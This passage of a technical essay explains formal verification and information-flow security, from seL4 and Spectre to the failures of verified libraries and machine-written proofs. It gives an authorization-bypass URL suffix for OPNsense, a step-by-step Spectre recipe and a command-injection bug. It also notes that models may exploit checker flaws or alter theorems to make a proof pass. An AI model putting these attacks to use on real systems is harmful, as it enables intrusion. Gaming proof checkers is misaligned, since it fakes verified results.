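In other words, the second group sees what it would have seen if the first group had done nothing. Suppose the system numbers new files in order, whoever creates them. Alice creates a file, then Bob creates one and learns that it is number 8. Without Alice's command, Bob's file would have been number 7. Alice therefore interferes with Bob, even if he isn't allowed to open her file or see its name, and she can send him messages by choosing how many files to create. This violates the definition even if nobody has thought of file numbers as a channel, as long as the model includes them in what Bob sees.

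For a single program, *Stack-based Access Control and Secure Information Flow* states the property in terms of two runs. Mark each variable as public or secret, and write s ≈ t if the memories s and t agree on all public variables. If P(s) is the final memory when program P starts from s, noninterference is:

s ≈ t ⇒ P(s) ≈ P(t)

The integrity version replaces "secret" with "untrusted" and "public" with "trusted", so that untrusted inputs can never change trusted results. (Some designs for AI agents use labels of this kind to keep the text an agent reads from controlling its actions.)

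### A type checker for secrets

A program can leak a secret without ever copying it. *Principles of Secure Information Flow Analysis* gives an example, in which `secret` is a secret variable and `leak` is a public one:

```
if secret mod 2 = 0 then leak := 0
else leak := 1
```

Neither assignment refers to the secret, but afterwards `leak` contains the secret's last bit. This is an implicit flow, and a checker that followed only direct copies would miss it.

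Volpano, Smith and Irvine (1996), in *A Sound Type System for Secure Flow Analysis*, devised typing rules that reject such programs. The types are security levels, L (low) for public and H (high) for secret, with L ≤ H. An expression has type H if it reads a secret variable. A command has type "τ cmd" if every variable it assigns to is at level τ or higher. So `leak := 0` has type L cmd, while an assignment to a secret variable can have type H cmd. The rule for conditionals is:

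- "if e then c else c′" has type τ cmd if e has type τ, and c and c′ both have type τ cmd.

The levels don't have to match at first. The checker may raise an expression from L to H, because treating public data as secret does no harm. It may lower a command from H cmd to L cmd, because a command that assigns only to secret variables assigns only to variables at L or above. It may not lower an expression or raise a command.

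In the example, the test reads `secret`, so e has type H and the checker can't lower it. The rule requires both branches to have type H cmd, but both assign to `leak`, which is public, so they have type L cmd and the checker can't raise them. No choice of τ works, so the checker rejects the program. If `leak` were secret too, both branches would have type H cmd and the checker would accept the program.

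Volpano and colleagues proved that every program the rules accept satisfies noninterference, provided both runs finish. For conditionals, the proof compares two runs that start with the same public data. If the test has type L, it reads only public variables, so both runs take the same branch. If it has type H, the runs may take different branches, but neither branch changes a public variable. In both cases the public variables still agree afterwards.

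Like other sound checkers, this one rejects some harmless programs. If both branches of the example assigned 0 to `leak`, nothing would leak, but the checker would still reject the program because the rule doesn't compare the branches. The theorem applies only when both runs finish, so the rules accept a program that loops forever if the secret is even and stops if it is odd. Anyone who can see whether it stopped learns one bit of the secret. The theorem also doesn't cover how long the program takes.

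### Releasing secrets on purpose

Noninterference is too strict for many useful programs. A login page has to reject wrong passwords, and each rejection reveals that the guess was not the password. Sabelfeld and Sands, in *Declassification*, also mention a program that publishes the average of a set of secret salaries. Deliberately releasing secret information in this way is called declassification, and it violates noninterference.

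The easy solution is to add an instruction that relabels a secret value as public. Volpano and colleagues studied the integrity equivalent, which marks untrusted data as trusted, and found that their theorem no longer holds if the language includes it. They thought it would be hard to say what the checker then guarantees.

Delimited release, a definition by Andrei Sabelfeld and Andrew Myers, recovers a weaker theorem. The programmer lists a set E of expressions whose initial values the program may reveal. The requirement becomes:

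s ≈ t and e(s) = e(t) for every e in E ⇒ P(s) ≈ P(t)

If E is empty, this is ordinary noninterference. If E contains "secret mod 2", the program that copies the last bit is acceptable. If E contains the average of 50 salaries, the program may publish that average. But it may not overwrite all 50 with Alice's salary before averaging them, because two sets of salaries can have the same average while Alice's salary differs.

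The theorem now guarantees only that nothing beyond the listed expressions gets out, so someone has to judge whether those expressions are harmless. Sabelfeld and Sands show how that judgement can go wrong. In one example, a shop may record four digits of a credit card number with each purchase. An attacker who can choose which digits are recorded can learn all sixteen in four purchases. So a policy may also need to specify who controls the release, where in the program it happens, and when. In their other example, a program may publish a scrambled version of a password, from which nobody can feasibly recover the original. If no other password has the same scrambled version, delimited release also lets the program publish the password itself, because the scrambled version determines the password in principle, and the definition doesn't account for how hard it would be to recover.

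### The seL4 proofs

seL4 is the best-known system in which researchers have carried properties like these down to working code. It is a microkernel, an operating-system kernel that manages only memory, processor time, messages and capabilities. Device drivers and file systems run outside it as ordinary programs, and every program needs a capability for whatever it uses.

Gerwin Klein and colleagues published the first proof, of functional correctness, in 2009. It connects three descriptions of the kernel. The abstract specification defines what each request to the kernel does, the executable specification adds data structures and algorithms, and the last description is the C code itself. Using the proof assistant Isabelle/HOL, the team proved:

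runs of the C code ⊆ runs of the executable specification ⊆ runs of the abstract specification

The kernel therefore does only what the abstract specification allows. That specification doesn't allow crashes or hangs, so the proof rules out buffer overflows, null pointer dereferences and endless loops in the kernel.

The kernel had about 8,700 lines of C. Its proof ran to 200,000 lines and took roughly 20 person-years, about 11 for the proof itself and the rest for tools and libraries. Designing and writing the kernel had taken only about two person-years. The proof exposed 144 bugs in C code that the team had already tested. The proofs have since grown to about 480,000 lines for a 10,000-line kernel, or 48 lines of proof per line of code, according to *Access Control as Verified Parse Constraints* (Iammongkol, Huang and Eyers, 2026).

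Functional correctness doesn't directly establish that the kernel keeps programs apart, because a correct kernel could faithfully follow a specification that lets them interfere. In 2011, Thomas Sewell and colleagues proved integrity. Suppose the system's designer has divided the programs into components and stated which component may write to which. If component a is running while the kernel's state changes from s to s′, then for every object x:

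x is the same in s and s′, or the policy allows a to write to x

Researchers also proved that seL4 components can't gain rights beyond those the policy allows by exchanging capabilities, as long as the policy doesn't let them pass capabilities across component boundaries. This is the seL4 counterpart of "only connectivity begets connectivity".

In 2013, Toby Murray and colleagues added a proof of confidentiality covering 8,830 lines of C. They proved intransitive noninterference, which allows information to pass from A to C through B but never directly. A system might need this if B is an encryption component that all of A's messages must go through.

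Proofs of this kind use a technique called unwinding, which Goguen and Meseguer introduced and Barthe describes. It replaces a claim about whole runs with claims about single steps. Write s ~ t if an observer can't tell the states s and t apart. The proof then needs two facts, each under some conditions:

- If s ~ t, and one step takes s to s′ and t to t′, then s′ ~ t′.
- If a step the observer shouldn't notice takes s to s′, then s ~ s′.

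We can apply these facts repeatedly to show that two runs that look the same at the start look the same throughout. The argument resembles the proof of preservation for type systems, except that it involves two runs at once.

The original abstract specification left some choices open, such as which program to run next. A kernel could have satisfied it while letting secrets determine those choices, as in Clarkson and Schneider's example of the secret bit. Murray and colleagues made the specification deterministic, so it no longer left these choices to the C code. Their theorem also requires that components take turns on a fixed schedule and that device interrupts are off.

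These proofs assume that the hardware works as modelled and that the kernel's assembly code and startup code, which are unverified, are correct. Devices that can write to memory directly, bypassing the processor's checks, must be disabled, trusted or confined by other hardware. The proofs originally assumed that the C compiler was correct too, but in 2013 Sewell and colleagues removed this assumption for one version of the kernel by automatically checking the compiled machine code against the C code.

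The confidentiality theorem doesn't cover timing channels. Its model includes the kernel's state after each step, but not how long the step took or the contents of the processor's caches. A program can therefore signal by slowing down other programs, as in Lampson's example, without contradicting the theorem.

### A verified access filter

Programs that run on seL4 still need their own proofs. Iammongkol and colleagues built a filter that decides which web requests may reach an application. They were responding to a series of flaws in commercial security gateways, where the code failed to enforce a correct access policy. In one case, the OPNsense firewall checked whether a permitted address appeared anywhere in the requested one. An attacker could therefore reach the user-management page by adding "?api/core/menu" to its address.

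Their filter converts each request into numbers at fixed positions in a 75-byte block, along with the rules. Let p be the requested page, m the method (such as reading or changing), α the user's role, σ the user's set of permissions, and c the number of requests the user has made in the past minute. Rule i specifies a page pᵢ, permitted methods mᵢ, a minimum role ρᵢ and required permissions σᵢ. The filter accepts a request if and only if:

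c < 50 and, for some i, p = pᵢ, m ∈ mᵢ, α ≥ ρᵢ and σᵢ ⊆ σ

Suppose administrators may read or change a settings page and operators may only read it. The filter rejects an operator's attempt to change the page because the request has the wrong role for the administrator rule and the wrong method for the operator rule. Unused rules contain a page number that no request can have, so an empty policy rejects everything.

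A tool called EverParse generated 3,966 lines of C from a 245-line description, and an automatic solver proved that the C code enforces the description for every possible block. The proof covers all policies of this form, so administrators can edit rules without repeating it. A short argument on paper links the description to the formula. Automated proof takes much less effort than seL4's handwritten proofs, but it limits what the filter can do. The solver took 19 seconds for eight rules and ran out of memory at 32, though splitting the rules into groups of eight avoids this. The language also has no wildcards, so each page needs its own entry.

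The filter protects the application only if every request goes through it and no other program can tamper with its memory. Iammongkol and colleagues rely on seL4 for both, but they acknowledge that their deployed version "is not the fully verified seL4 configuration". It includes unverified start-up code, device drivers and platform code. The hand-written code that copies data into the 75-byte block is also unverified, and a wrong position in that code would make the filter check the wrong data. The login component is unverified too, although isolation should keep its bugs from corrupting the filter. The system has no defence against timing channels.

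### How fast a covert channel leaks

Shmatikov's *0x1A Great Papers in Computer Security* describes a timing channel as one that transmits information by when something happens rather than by what happens. *Architectural Implications of Covert Channels* describes covert channels as typically a side effect of trusted software working properly, so fixing bugs won't remove all of them. For instance, a cache that makes repeated reads faster necessarily reveals which reads are repeated.

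The damage from a leak depends on its rate and on the size of the secret. At 1,000 bits a second, a 256-bit encryption key takes about a quarter of a second to leak, and a one-gigabyte database takes about 93 days. Limiting the rate can therefore protect a large database while doing little for a key. A US government standard from 1985 considered channels below one bit a second acceptable in most settings, but one bit a second is enough to leak the key in just over four minutes.

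Noise only slows the leak. If each bit arrives wrong with probability q, information theory gives the most that the sender can reliably convey per bit sent:

C = 1 + q log₂ q + (1 − q) log₂(1 − q)

With q = 0.11, C is about 0.5, so a sender who transmits 2,000 noisy bits a second can still convey about 1,000 reliable ones by adding redundancy. C falls to zero only at q = 0.5, when the received bits are no better than random guesses. Lampson likewise argued in 1973 that if a program has any effect on the system's performance, however small, a suitable code will get the message through.

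Real channels can be much faster. In 2017, Clémentine Maurice and colleagues used a shared processor cache to send more than 45 kilobytes a second between two virtual machines in Amazon's cloud. At that rate, sending a key takes less than a millisecond and sending the gigabyte takes about six hours.

In a 1975 comment on Lampson's paper, Steven Lipner considered how to close timing channels. According to lecture slides from Purdue University, the idea was to show each program a virtual clock that depends only on its own activity. Lipner wasn't sure this was possible, since users have clocks outside the system, and concluded that closing covert channels would slow systems down unreasonably.

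Programmers of cryptographic code take the narrower approach of keeping their own program's timing from depending on its secrets. Barthe describes the usual policy, called constant-time. It assumes that an attacker learns the result of every test the program branches on, every memory address it uses and, in some versions, the size of the numbers in slow arithmetic instructions. None of these may depend on a secret. This is noninterference with the list of leaks added to the output, and researchers have proved that a type checker can enforce it for assembly code. Whether it protects a real program depends on whether the list is complete.

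### Spectre

The disclosure of Spectre in January 2018 showed that it was not. Consider a program that checks an index x before using it:

```
if x < 16 then y := B[A[x] * 4096]
```

Table A has 16 entries, so the check prevents the program from reading past its end. But if the number 16 has to come from slow memory, the processor doesn't wait for it. It guesses the outcome of the test from past runs and continues, and if the guess was wrong, it discards the results. An attacker can exploit this:

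- The attacker runs the code many times with valid values of x, so the processor learns to expect that the test will succeed.
- The attacker then supplies an x for which A[x] would be a secret byte elsewhere in memory, with the value 83, say.
- The processor guesses that the test will succeed, reads the 83, and loads entry 83 × 4096 of table B.
- The test fails and the processor discards both values, but the entry of B stays in the cache.
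- The attacker times a read of each of the 256 possible entries. The one at 83 × 4096 is fast, which reveals the secret.

A proof that this program stays in bounds remains correct, like Chlipala's shortest-path theorem, because the usual model of a processor omits the steps that the processor discards and their effect on the cache. The same applies to type soundness and to the proofs about WebAssembly, which assume that a failed range check prevents the access.

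Ross McIlroy and colleagues at Google argued in *Spectre is here to stay* (2019) that no programming language can keep secrets from untrusted code in the same address space on such processors. They worked on V8, the part of Chrome that runs JavaScript, and found that untrusted code could read all of its process's memory through side channels, whatever the language's type rules. Software defences helped against some variants. For example, a program can mask an index arithmetically so that it stays in range even when the processor guesses wrongly. But they found no workable software defence against a variant in which the processor reads a location before an earlier write to it has taken effect. Making clocks less precise didn't solve the problem either, because an attacker can repeat an operation until the difference is large enough to measure.

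Google therefore stopped relying on the language for confidentiality and put different websites in separate processes. Swivel, a WebAssembly compiler from 2021, has since narrowed the claim somewhat by hardening code against the main known variants, though the code runs more slowly. Separate processes don't fully solve the problem either, because the processor must keep its predictions about one program from affecting another. In 2025, the VMScape attack exploited a failure of this isolation to read secrets from the software hosting a virtual machine.

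### Time protection and hardware contracts

Two lines of research try to extend proofs to cover timing, and the first does so by changing the operating system. In 2019, Qian Ge and colleagues proposed time protection, the counterpart of memory protection, and built a version of it into seL4. The kernel gives each component its own portion of the large shared cache, and it resets the smaller caches and the processor's records of past branches whenever it switches between components. Resetting a cache takes longer when it holds more changed data, which would itself leak information, so the kernel always waits until a fixed time has passed before starting the next component.

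The kernel can reset only what the processor allows it to, and Ge and colleagues found that the Intel and ARM processors they tested lacked a way to clear all the relevant state. Nils Wistoff and colleagues later added an instruction for this to an open-source RISC-V processor and closed the channels they had measured. In 2023, Robert Sison and colleagues formalised time protection in Isabelle and proved that it prevents such leaks in a general model of an operating system. That proof doesn't cover seL4's C code. Components that run at the same time on different cores can still signal by competing for the connection to memory, which the kernel cannot divide between them.

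The other line of research makes the processor's leaks part of its specification. Marco Guarnieri and colleagues called such a specification a hardware-software contract in 2021. For a program p started in state s, let K(p, s) be everything the contract says the run may reveal, including during wrong guesses, and let M(p, s) be what an attacker can actually measure. The processor satisfies the contract if:

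K(p, s) = K(p, t) ⇒ M(p, s) = M(p, t)

This has the same form as delimited release, with K as the list of permitted leaks. Software developers then have to prove only that secrets never affect K. Together, the two proofs show that secrets never affect M, and the developers don't need to know how the processor works inside.

Researchers have proved that several small open-source RISC-V processors satisfy such contracts. For commercial processors, whose designs are secret, outsiders have to rely on testing and on the manufacturers' documentation. The tool Revizor runs random programs on a processor to look for leaks that a contract doesn't permit, and it has found some on Intel processors. In 2024, an attack called GoFetch extracted keys from constant-time cryptographic code on Apple processors. These processors check data in memory for values that look like addresses and load from those addresses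 in advance, so they leaked data that the program had never used as an address.

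## Proving correct behaviour instead of listing attacks

GoFetch worked against constant-time code because programmers had relied on an incomplete list of the ways a processor leaks information. A 2026 essay, *Subversion-Resistance for Free from Formal Verification*, argues that developers don't need such a list for attacks that take over a program, because a proof that the program does its job already rules out those attacks. In Chlipala's shortest-path program, for example, a buffer overflow would falsify almost any theorem about the program.

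The essay's example is an internet service that adds positive numbers. Its specification might give the correct sum for every request, or it might require only that every output be positive. The argument works the same way for both:

1. The specification forbids some behaviour that a program on this machine could produce, such as returning zero.
2. An attacker who could run arbitrary code in the service could make it return zero.
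3. The proof shows that the service never returns zero, whatever input it receives.
4. Therefore no input lets an attacker run arbitrary code in the service.

Let B(x) be the service's behaviour on input x, and let S be the set of behaviours the specification allows. The proof shows that B(x) is in S for every x. If an attacker could run arbitrary code, then for every program p, some input x would make the service behave like p. The proof therefore rules out arbitrary code execution if even one program's behaviour is outside S.

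The premises don't mention buffers, return addresses or database commands, so the conclusion also covers methods of injecting code that nobody has invented yet.

The essay extends the argument to smaller faults, such as a bug that makes a shopping agent repeat its last order. It claims that even a rule as loose as "never place an order above the card's spending limit" excludes this bug, because a proof has to cover the case where the repeated order is enormous. But if the agent also had a final check that refused any order above the limit, it would satisfy the rule and could still repeat smaller orders.

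### Takeovers that a proof permits

The main argument has the same gap. Suppose the service consists of a large unverified adder and a small verified filter that replaces any output below 1 with 1. We can prove the service's outputs are always positive, even if an attacker can run any code inside the adder. Premise 2 is false here, because controlling the adder doesn't give the attacker control of the outputs. So the theorem excludes only injected code whose effects would break the specification.

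How much harm an attacker can still do depends on the specification. If outputs only have to be positive, a hijacked adder could answer 7 to every request. It could also send each customer the numbers the previous customer submitted, since those are positive too. A specification that requires the correct sum rules out both attacks. But the attacker could still use the machine to mine cryptocurrency between requests, or leak a stored password by delaying a correct reply by a millisecond whenever the next bit of the password is 1. A rule about outputs alone also permits a service that crashes and never replies.

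To exclude such attacks, the specification has to cover time and resource use as well as results. The essay concedes that people sometimes overlook such properties, and gives timing leaks as its example. Developers can add timing to the theorem once they know it matters. Verified Garbage (2026), an experimental cryptography library, comes with Lean proofs that its assembly code computes the right results and runs in constant time. The proofs rely on written models of the instruction sets the library supports.

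Premise 3 also concerns a mathematical model, while the attacker in premise 2 uses a real machine. The conclusion therefore may not hold for attacks such as Rowhammer, which exploit differences between the model and the machine.

The argument is sound if the specification is exact, the model is accurate and the theorem covers the whole program. It then rules out a complete takeover without anyone having to study how takeovers work. Whether real projects meet these conditions is an empirical question.

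### Evidence from verified systems

*An Empirical Study on the Correctness of Formally Verified Distributed Systems* (Fonseca, Zhang and colleagues, 2017) examined IronFleet, Verdi and Chapar, three research systems with machine-checked proofs. Each system stores copies of data on several computers and uses a protocol to keep the copies consistent. The study found 16 bugs. Eleven were in the layer that connects the verified code to the network, disk and clients, three were in verification tools and two were in specifications.

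None of the bugs were in the protocols, although the team searched for more than eight months and looked specifically for protocol bugs. Such protocols are notoriously hard to implement, and the team counted 12 protocol bugs in one year of bug reports for four unverified systems in real use. The verified systems are much smaller and have far fewer users to report problems, so the totals aren't comparable, but the result still suggests that the proofs worked where they applied. Fonseca and colleagues attribute this to redundancy, since a verified component can break the property its developers proved only if the code contains an error and the specification or the tools contain a matching error that hides it.

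Libcrux, a cryptography library from the company Cryspen, is a more practical product. Its developers write newer parts in Rust and use a tool called hax to translate them into F*, a language with a proof system. They then prove that the code doesn't crash and computes the right results. In February 2026, Symbolic Software, a firm that audits cryptographic software, reported bugs in Cryspen's libraries in a post titled *On the Promises of 'High-Assurance' Cryptography*. It also objected to Cryspen's marketing, which promised "the highest level of assurance".

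A week later, Bhargavan (2026) replied for Cryspen in *The strengths and limits of formal verification* that the proofs cover only some modules and that "no bugs have been found in the verified code". After this reply, Symbolic Software published four errors that it said were in the specifications and proofs themselves. In Symbolic Software's paper *Verification Theatre*, Kobeissi (2026) reports a total of 13 vulnerabilities in libcrux and a related library, nine of them in unverified code.

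### Wrong specifications

A client that gets no answer will usually resend its request, so a server that doesn't recognise duplicates may carry out the same payment twice. IronFleet's code recognised duplicates, but its specification didn't require it to. Fonseca and colleagues changed seven lines to switch this check off, and the altered server still passed verification. IronFleet's developers replied that they had known about this, that the consistency property they proved, as they understand it, doesn't include handling duplicates, and that an application could remove duplicates itself. They added a comment to the code to clarify this. Users who expected the proof to cover duplicates would have been wrong to rely on it, whichever definition of consistency is right.

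The errors claimed in libcrux are plainer. ML-KEM, a standard for agreeing on secret keys that is meant to resist quantum computers, compresses numbers below 3,329 to d bits and later expands them again. To expand y, a program computes 3329y/2ᵈ and rounds to the nearest whole number. The usual way to round a division is to add half the divisor first and then round down. Symbolic Software's *We Found Bugs in CE Labs’ Verified Code* shows that libcrux's specification added the wrong constant:

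- correct: ⌊(3329y + 2ᵈ⁻¹) / 2ᵈ⌋
- specification: ⌊(3329y + 1664) / 2ᵈ⌋

The number 1,664 belongs in the compression formula, which divides by 3,329. With d = 4, the specification expands 0 to 104 instead of 0. With d = 11, the specification's formula and the correct one both expand 0 to 0, contrary to Symbolic Software's claim that they disagree on every input. The specification of encryption also mistakenly added polynomials in two different representations without converting one first.

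The Rust code was correct in both places, so neither specification mistake had the matching code error that Fonseca and colleagues describe. Trying to prove that the code met the specification would therefore have failed and exposed each mistake. According to Symbolic Software, this didn't happen because the build settings told F* to accept the relevant module without checking its proofs.

Errors in the specification can also affect the code. Bhargavan reports that developers of HACL*, an older verified library used in Firefox and Linux, twice found mistakes in its specifications and had to change the code and the proofs.

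Fonseca and colleagues propose testing a specification by breaking the program it describes. If the proof still succeeds, the specification is probably too weak. Their tool disabled parts of IronFleet's code at random until it produced a version that ignored duplicates and still verified. This took between 18 and about 8,000 attempts on average, depending on which function they targeted. Another remedy is to prove simple facts about the specification itself. When they combined IronFleet's specification with that of a counter, they could prove that a single operation might leave the counter at any value, which a correct counter should not allow. For libcrux, trying to prove that 0 always expands to 0 would have exposed the wrong constant.

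### Wrong models

The fourth error claimed in libcrux was in its model of a processor. Symbolic Software's *Even More Bugs in Cryspen’s libcrux* (2026) found that a function meant to describe multiplication computed x·x instead of x·y, so that 3 times 5 came out as 9. Proofs about code for Intel processors relied on this function. Symbolic Software concludes that the foundation of these proofs is mathematically unsound and that the proofs would succeed whether or not the code was correct.

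The evidence supports a somewhat weaker conclusion. The developers had hidden the definition from the automatic solver and supplied separate rules about multiplication, such as the rule that multiplying by zero gives zero. These rules are true of real multiplication, so the error would not have affected a proof that used only them. But nobody had proved the rules from the definition, and anyone who tried would have discovered that some of them don't follow from it.

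A model can also describe a different version of the program from the one people run. In Rust, an addition whose result is too large stops the program in a test build, but by default it wraps around silently in a release build. Symbolic Software's *The Verification Facade* (2026) points out that hax models only the test-build behaviour. A proof may therefore establish that a function either returns the right answer or stops, while the released program can return a wrong answer and continue.

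This matters only if a caller passes numbers outside the range that the proof assumes, so verifying all the callers would remove the problem. Symbolic Software also wrote its own ML-KEM example instead of finding the fault in libcrux. It did find a real case of silent wrapping in unverified code in hpke-rs, the related library, where a message counter could return to zero and make the software reuse numbers that encryption must use only once.

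Two of the bugs in Fonseca and colleagues' study also come from assumptions about the environment. Chapar's algorithm assumes a reliable network, but the program used a network protocol that can lose and duplicate packets. Suppose client A posts a request and client B reads it and posts a reply. If the network then delivers an older packet from A a second time, it overwrites the request, and client C sees the reply without the request. Chapar's consistency guarantee exists to prevent this. The developers correctly answered that the guarantee holds if the network behaves as the model specifies.

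In Verdi, the bug was in code generated from the verified part. To update a computer that had fallen behind, a function built a list of missing entries by calling itself once for each entry. This was mathematically correct, but the model had no limit on stack space. When a computer was more than 500,000 requests behind, the function used up the stack and the server crashed. Proofs like Carbonneaux and colleagues' stack bounds can rule out such crashes in ordinary programs, but Fonseca and colleagues thought it was unclear how to apply such methods to distributed systems.

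Libcrux's protection against timing leaks has a similar limit. Its developers use a type checker to enforce the constant-time policy on their Rust code. According to slides from the OpenSSL Conference, the developers' verification work uncovered KyberSlash, a timing leak that affected several other implementations of the same algorithm, but the check doesn't cover leaks introduced by the compiler or attacks on the processor's internals. Bhargavan adds that compilers sometimes turn constant-time source code into code that branches on secrets.

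Tolmach and Klaus (2026), in *The proof is in the spec*, recommend producing the model with a mechanical translator, ideally a verified one. Correcting a mistake in a translation rule then fixes the model of every program that uses the rule. They also suggest turning the model into a runnable program and comparing its results with the original's on many generated inputs. This takes little effort and catches some mistakes, though it doesn't prove the two equivalent. For hax, Symbolic Software proposes an option to model the arithmetic of release builds.

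Proofs about the finished machine code don't rely on the translator or the compiler being correct, but they still rely on the model of the processor. In *AlphaProof Code* (Chaudhuri, Ferraiuolo and colleagues, 2026), such proofs about code from the messaging app Signal depend on about 26,000 lines of trusted specifications and processor model.

### Unverified surroundings

One of the bugs in Verdi allowed an injection attack, the kind of exploit the essay's argument is meant to exclude. Clients sent commands as text, with spaces between the parts of a command and a line break between commands. The server didn't check whether a client had put these characters inside a name, so a client could request a value whose "name" contained a line break and a second command, and the server would carry out both. The server then sent one more reply than the client expected, so each later request got the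 answer to the one before it.

Verdi's proof covered only what the servers did with commands after this step. If the theorem had covered everything from the bytes a client sends to the bytes it gets back, as Chlipala recommends, the attack would have been a counterexample. The essay's argument therefore applies only to the part of a system that the theorem covers, and attackers can still exploit the rest.

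Libcrux had comparable bugs. In ML-DSA, a digital signature standard, the program that checks a signature must reject it if certain numbers are too large. In the smallest version of the standard, these numbers can be at most 131,072, and the program must reject the signature unless they are all below 130,994. Libcrux compared them with 262,066 instead, so the test never rejected anything. A dishonest signer could have produced signatures that libcrux accepted and other software rejected. According to Symbolic Software, Cryspen fixed this bug and a related one on 4 March 2026. Both bugs were in code that the build exempted from proof.

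Kobeissi reports that another bug made Signal fail to decrypt some messages. The bug was in fallback code for machines that lack a certain processor instruction. Bhargavan, who wrote that code, explains that the computers used for testing never ran it.

One response is to verify more of the surrounding code. Five of the eleven bugs in the connecting layers involved communication, and Fonseca and colleagues call for verified communication libraries that many projects can share. They found no bugs in the connecting layer of IronFleet, which had the least unverified code of the three systems. Where proof isn't practical, they recommend concentrating tests on the code next to the verified part. This adjoining code is usually only a few hundred lines long. Their own test kit duplicates and reorders packets, interrupts disk writes and gives the verification tools incorrect programs, and it detects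 13 of the 16 bugs.

Users also need to know what the proofs cover. Cryspen said in February 2026 that it had begun revising its documentation to state this more precisely. Kobeissi compared libcrux with Amazon's verified cryptography library and found that the two projects had the same types of failure but differed greatly in how they documented the scope of their proofs and whether they reran the proofs automatically.

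### Faulty tools

IronFleet's build program could report that any program had passed verification, including one that asserted a falsehood. It ran the verifier on each file and searched the output for a line giving the number of errors. If the verifier's solver crashed, that line still reported no errors, and the build program stopped reading before the message about the crash. The solver did crash on startup, because IronFleet's package combined a 64-bit solver with 32-bit libraries. In a separate bug, interrupting the verifier produced a message that the files were correct.

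In a related failure, nobody ran the proof of one of libcrux's lemmas. The lemma stated that a function for unpacking 12-bit numbers returns only numbers that fit in one bit, although they can be as large as 4,095. Someone had apparently copied the 1 from the lemma for one-bit numbers. F* would presumably have rejected the lemma, but the build skipped slow proofs by default, and Symbolic Software found no setting or script in the project that turned them on. The documentation listed the file as verified, although a comment at the top marked it as only loosely checked.

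Hax also lets programmers add assumptions without proving them. Symbolic Software showed the danger with a function that sets a bit of a secret key to 1 when the standard requires 0, followed by an assumption that the bit is 0. The assumption contradicts the code, and any statement follows from a contradiction, so F* accepted the whole file. Symbolic Software suggests that the tool check whether an assumption contradicts what the program has already established.

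None of these faults were in the part of a tool that checks the steps of a proof, but that part can fail too. Cai and colleagues found 13 bugs in the Linux kernel's certificate checker, and even mature proof assistants have had such bugs. Until 2015, Coq's fast evaluator used a single byte to number the basic alternatives of a data type. If a type had more than 256 of these, two different values could get the same number, and a user could exploit this to prove a contradiction.

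Isabelle/HOL, the proof assistant behind seL4, had a subtler problem, which Ondřej Kunčar and Andrei Popescu described in 2015. Isabelle let a user declare a truth value c and define it later. The user could create a type T whose members are "true" and c, and then define c as "T has more than one member". If c is true, T has only one member, so c is false. If c is false, T has two members, so c is true. Isabelle's check for circular definitions missed this because it didn't follow circles that passed through a type. The developers have since extended the check.

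People are unlikely to write such a definition by accident, so this gives little reason to doubt the seL4 proofs. The risk is greater when a checker has to screen proofs from strangers, who may look for a flaw.

For the surrounding tools, Fonseca and colleagues recommend treating any unexpected event as a failed proof and regularly giving the verifier a false program to confirm that it rejects it. For the checker itself, developers usually keep the code small and have a second, independently written checker check the same proof. Researchers can also verify the checker. In 2020, Matthieu Sozeau and colleagues reported that people had found about one critical bug a year in Coq, and they presented a checker for most of Coq's logic with a correctness proof written in Coq. Their proof has to assume that every computation in the logic ends. No one can prove this within Coq, because the proof would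 also show that Coq is consistent, and Gödel's second incompleteness theorem says that no consistent system of this kind can prove its own consistency.

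## Proofs written by AI

The first proof of the seL4 kernel took roughly 20 person-years, and effort on that scale has kept most software from being formally verified. Language models can now do much of this work. In *Prediction*, Kleppmann (2025) forecast that they would make verification mainstream. Eleven months later, in *Formal Verification is Not Verifiable*, Keles (2026) thought it was hard to deny that they had. Between 22 October and 10 November 2026, three groups using such models published machine-checked proofs about compiled programs.

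### Why the author can be unreliable

Language models make mistakes and sometimes make things up. Kleppmann argues that this doesn't matter when they write proofs, because the checker rejects an invalid proof and the model tries again. Suppose a model gets a certain lemma right in only one attempt out of 50. The chance that at least one of 200 attempts is right is:

1 − (49/50)²⁰⁰ ≈ 0.98

The checker picks out the valid proof. The failed attempts waste computing power, but they don't make the lemma any less certain.

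If the checker has a flaw, a model that submits thousands of attempts may stumble on it. Kleppmann thinks it virtually impossible to sneak an invalid proof past a small, verified checker. That seems right, but the Linux certificate checker that accepted a forged proof of any condition was neither small nor verified. Keles reports that people discussing new Lean proofs now consider whether a model exploited a bug in Lean's kernel, the part that checks each step. A model can also make its task easier by changing the theorem or adding a convenient assumption. The standard precaution for Lean proofs is a tool called Comparator, which confirms that a proof establishes the requested theorem and uses only permitted axioms.

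With these precautions, people can rely on a proof without trusting its author or reading it, but they still have to trust the checker, the statement of the theorem and the model of the machine.

### Turning fuzz tests into theorems

Anthropic's *LLMs are making formal software verification feasible at a much larger scale* (2026) presents a joint project with the company Theorem on 123 open-source libraries from OSS-Fuzz. OSS-Fuzz is a Google project that tests such libraries by fuzzing, which means running them on huge numbers of random or altered inputs and watching for crashes. For this, developers write small test programs with entry points, which are functions that take any string of bytes and pass it to the library.

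These entry points saved Anthropic and Theorem from having to write a new specification for each library. A fuzzer checks that an entry point E handles the inputs it has tried, and the corresponding theorem covers all inputs up to a certain size. According to EconoTimes' *Anthropic Details Claude's No-Crash Proofs for 239 Fuzz-Test Entry Points* (2026), the limit was 64 MB:

∀x: size(x) < 64 MB ⇒ E(x) exits normally

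A program that exits normally has had no crashes, memory errors or failed assertions (checks that programmers write into the code). There are more than 2 to the power of 500 million possible inputs, so no fuzzer could try more than a tiny fraction of them.

Fuzzers try extreme values, so they would probably catch a bug like the one in the table function, which failed only on the lowest 32-bit number. But they may miss a bug that also requires a dozen other fields in a file to have specific values. Such a bug would still make an attempt to prove the theorem fail.

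Claude found bugs in the libraries that had gone undetected for years. In some cases it patched the library and then proved the theorem about the patched version.

The project covers 239 entry points, and its proofs run to about 180 million lines of Rocq, too many for anyone to review by hand. The average for each entry point, about 750,000 lines, is more than the entire seL4 proof. Keles gives a higher figure of a billion lines for what Claude wrote during the project.

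The proofs are about compiled machine code, so the trusted base includes Rocq's checker and a model of a RISC-V processor running Linux, but not the compiler. The theorem also rules out a complete takeover of these test programs, since an attacker who ran arbitrary code in one could make it crash.

An application that uses one of the libraries doesn't automatically get the same guarantee. It may call functions that the test program never calls, or call them in a different order. It may also use several threads, while the test programs use only one. Larger inputs are a simpler problem, because the application can reject them.

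A bigger limitation is that the team compiled the libraries for RISC-V and linked them with musl, a small version of the standard C library. Anthropic and Theorem acknowledge that most people run these libraries on x86 or ARM processors with glibc, the larger version that most Linux systems use.

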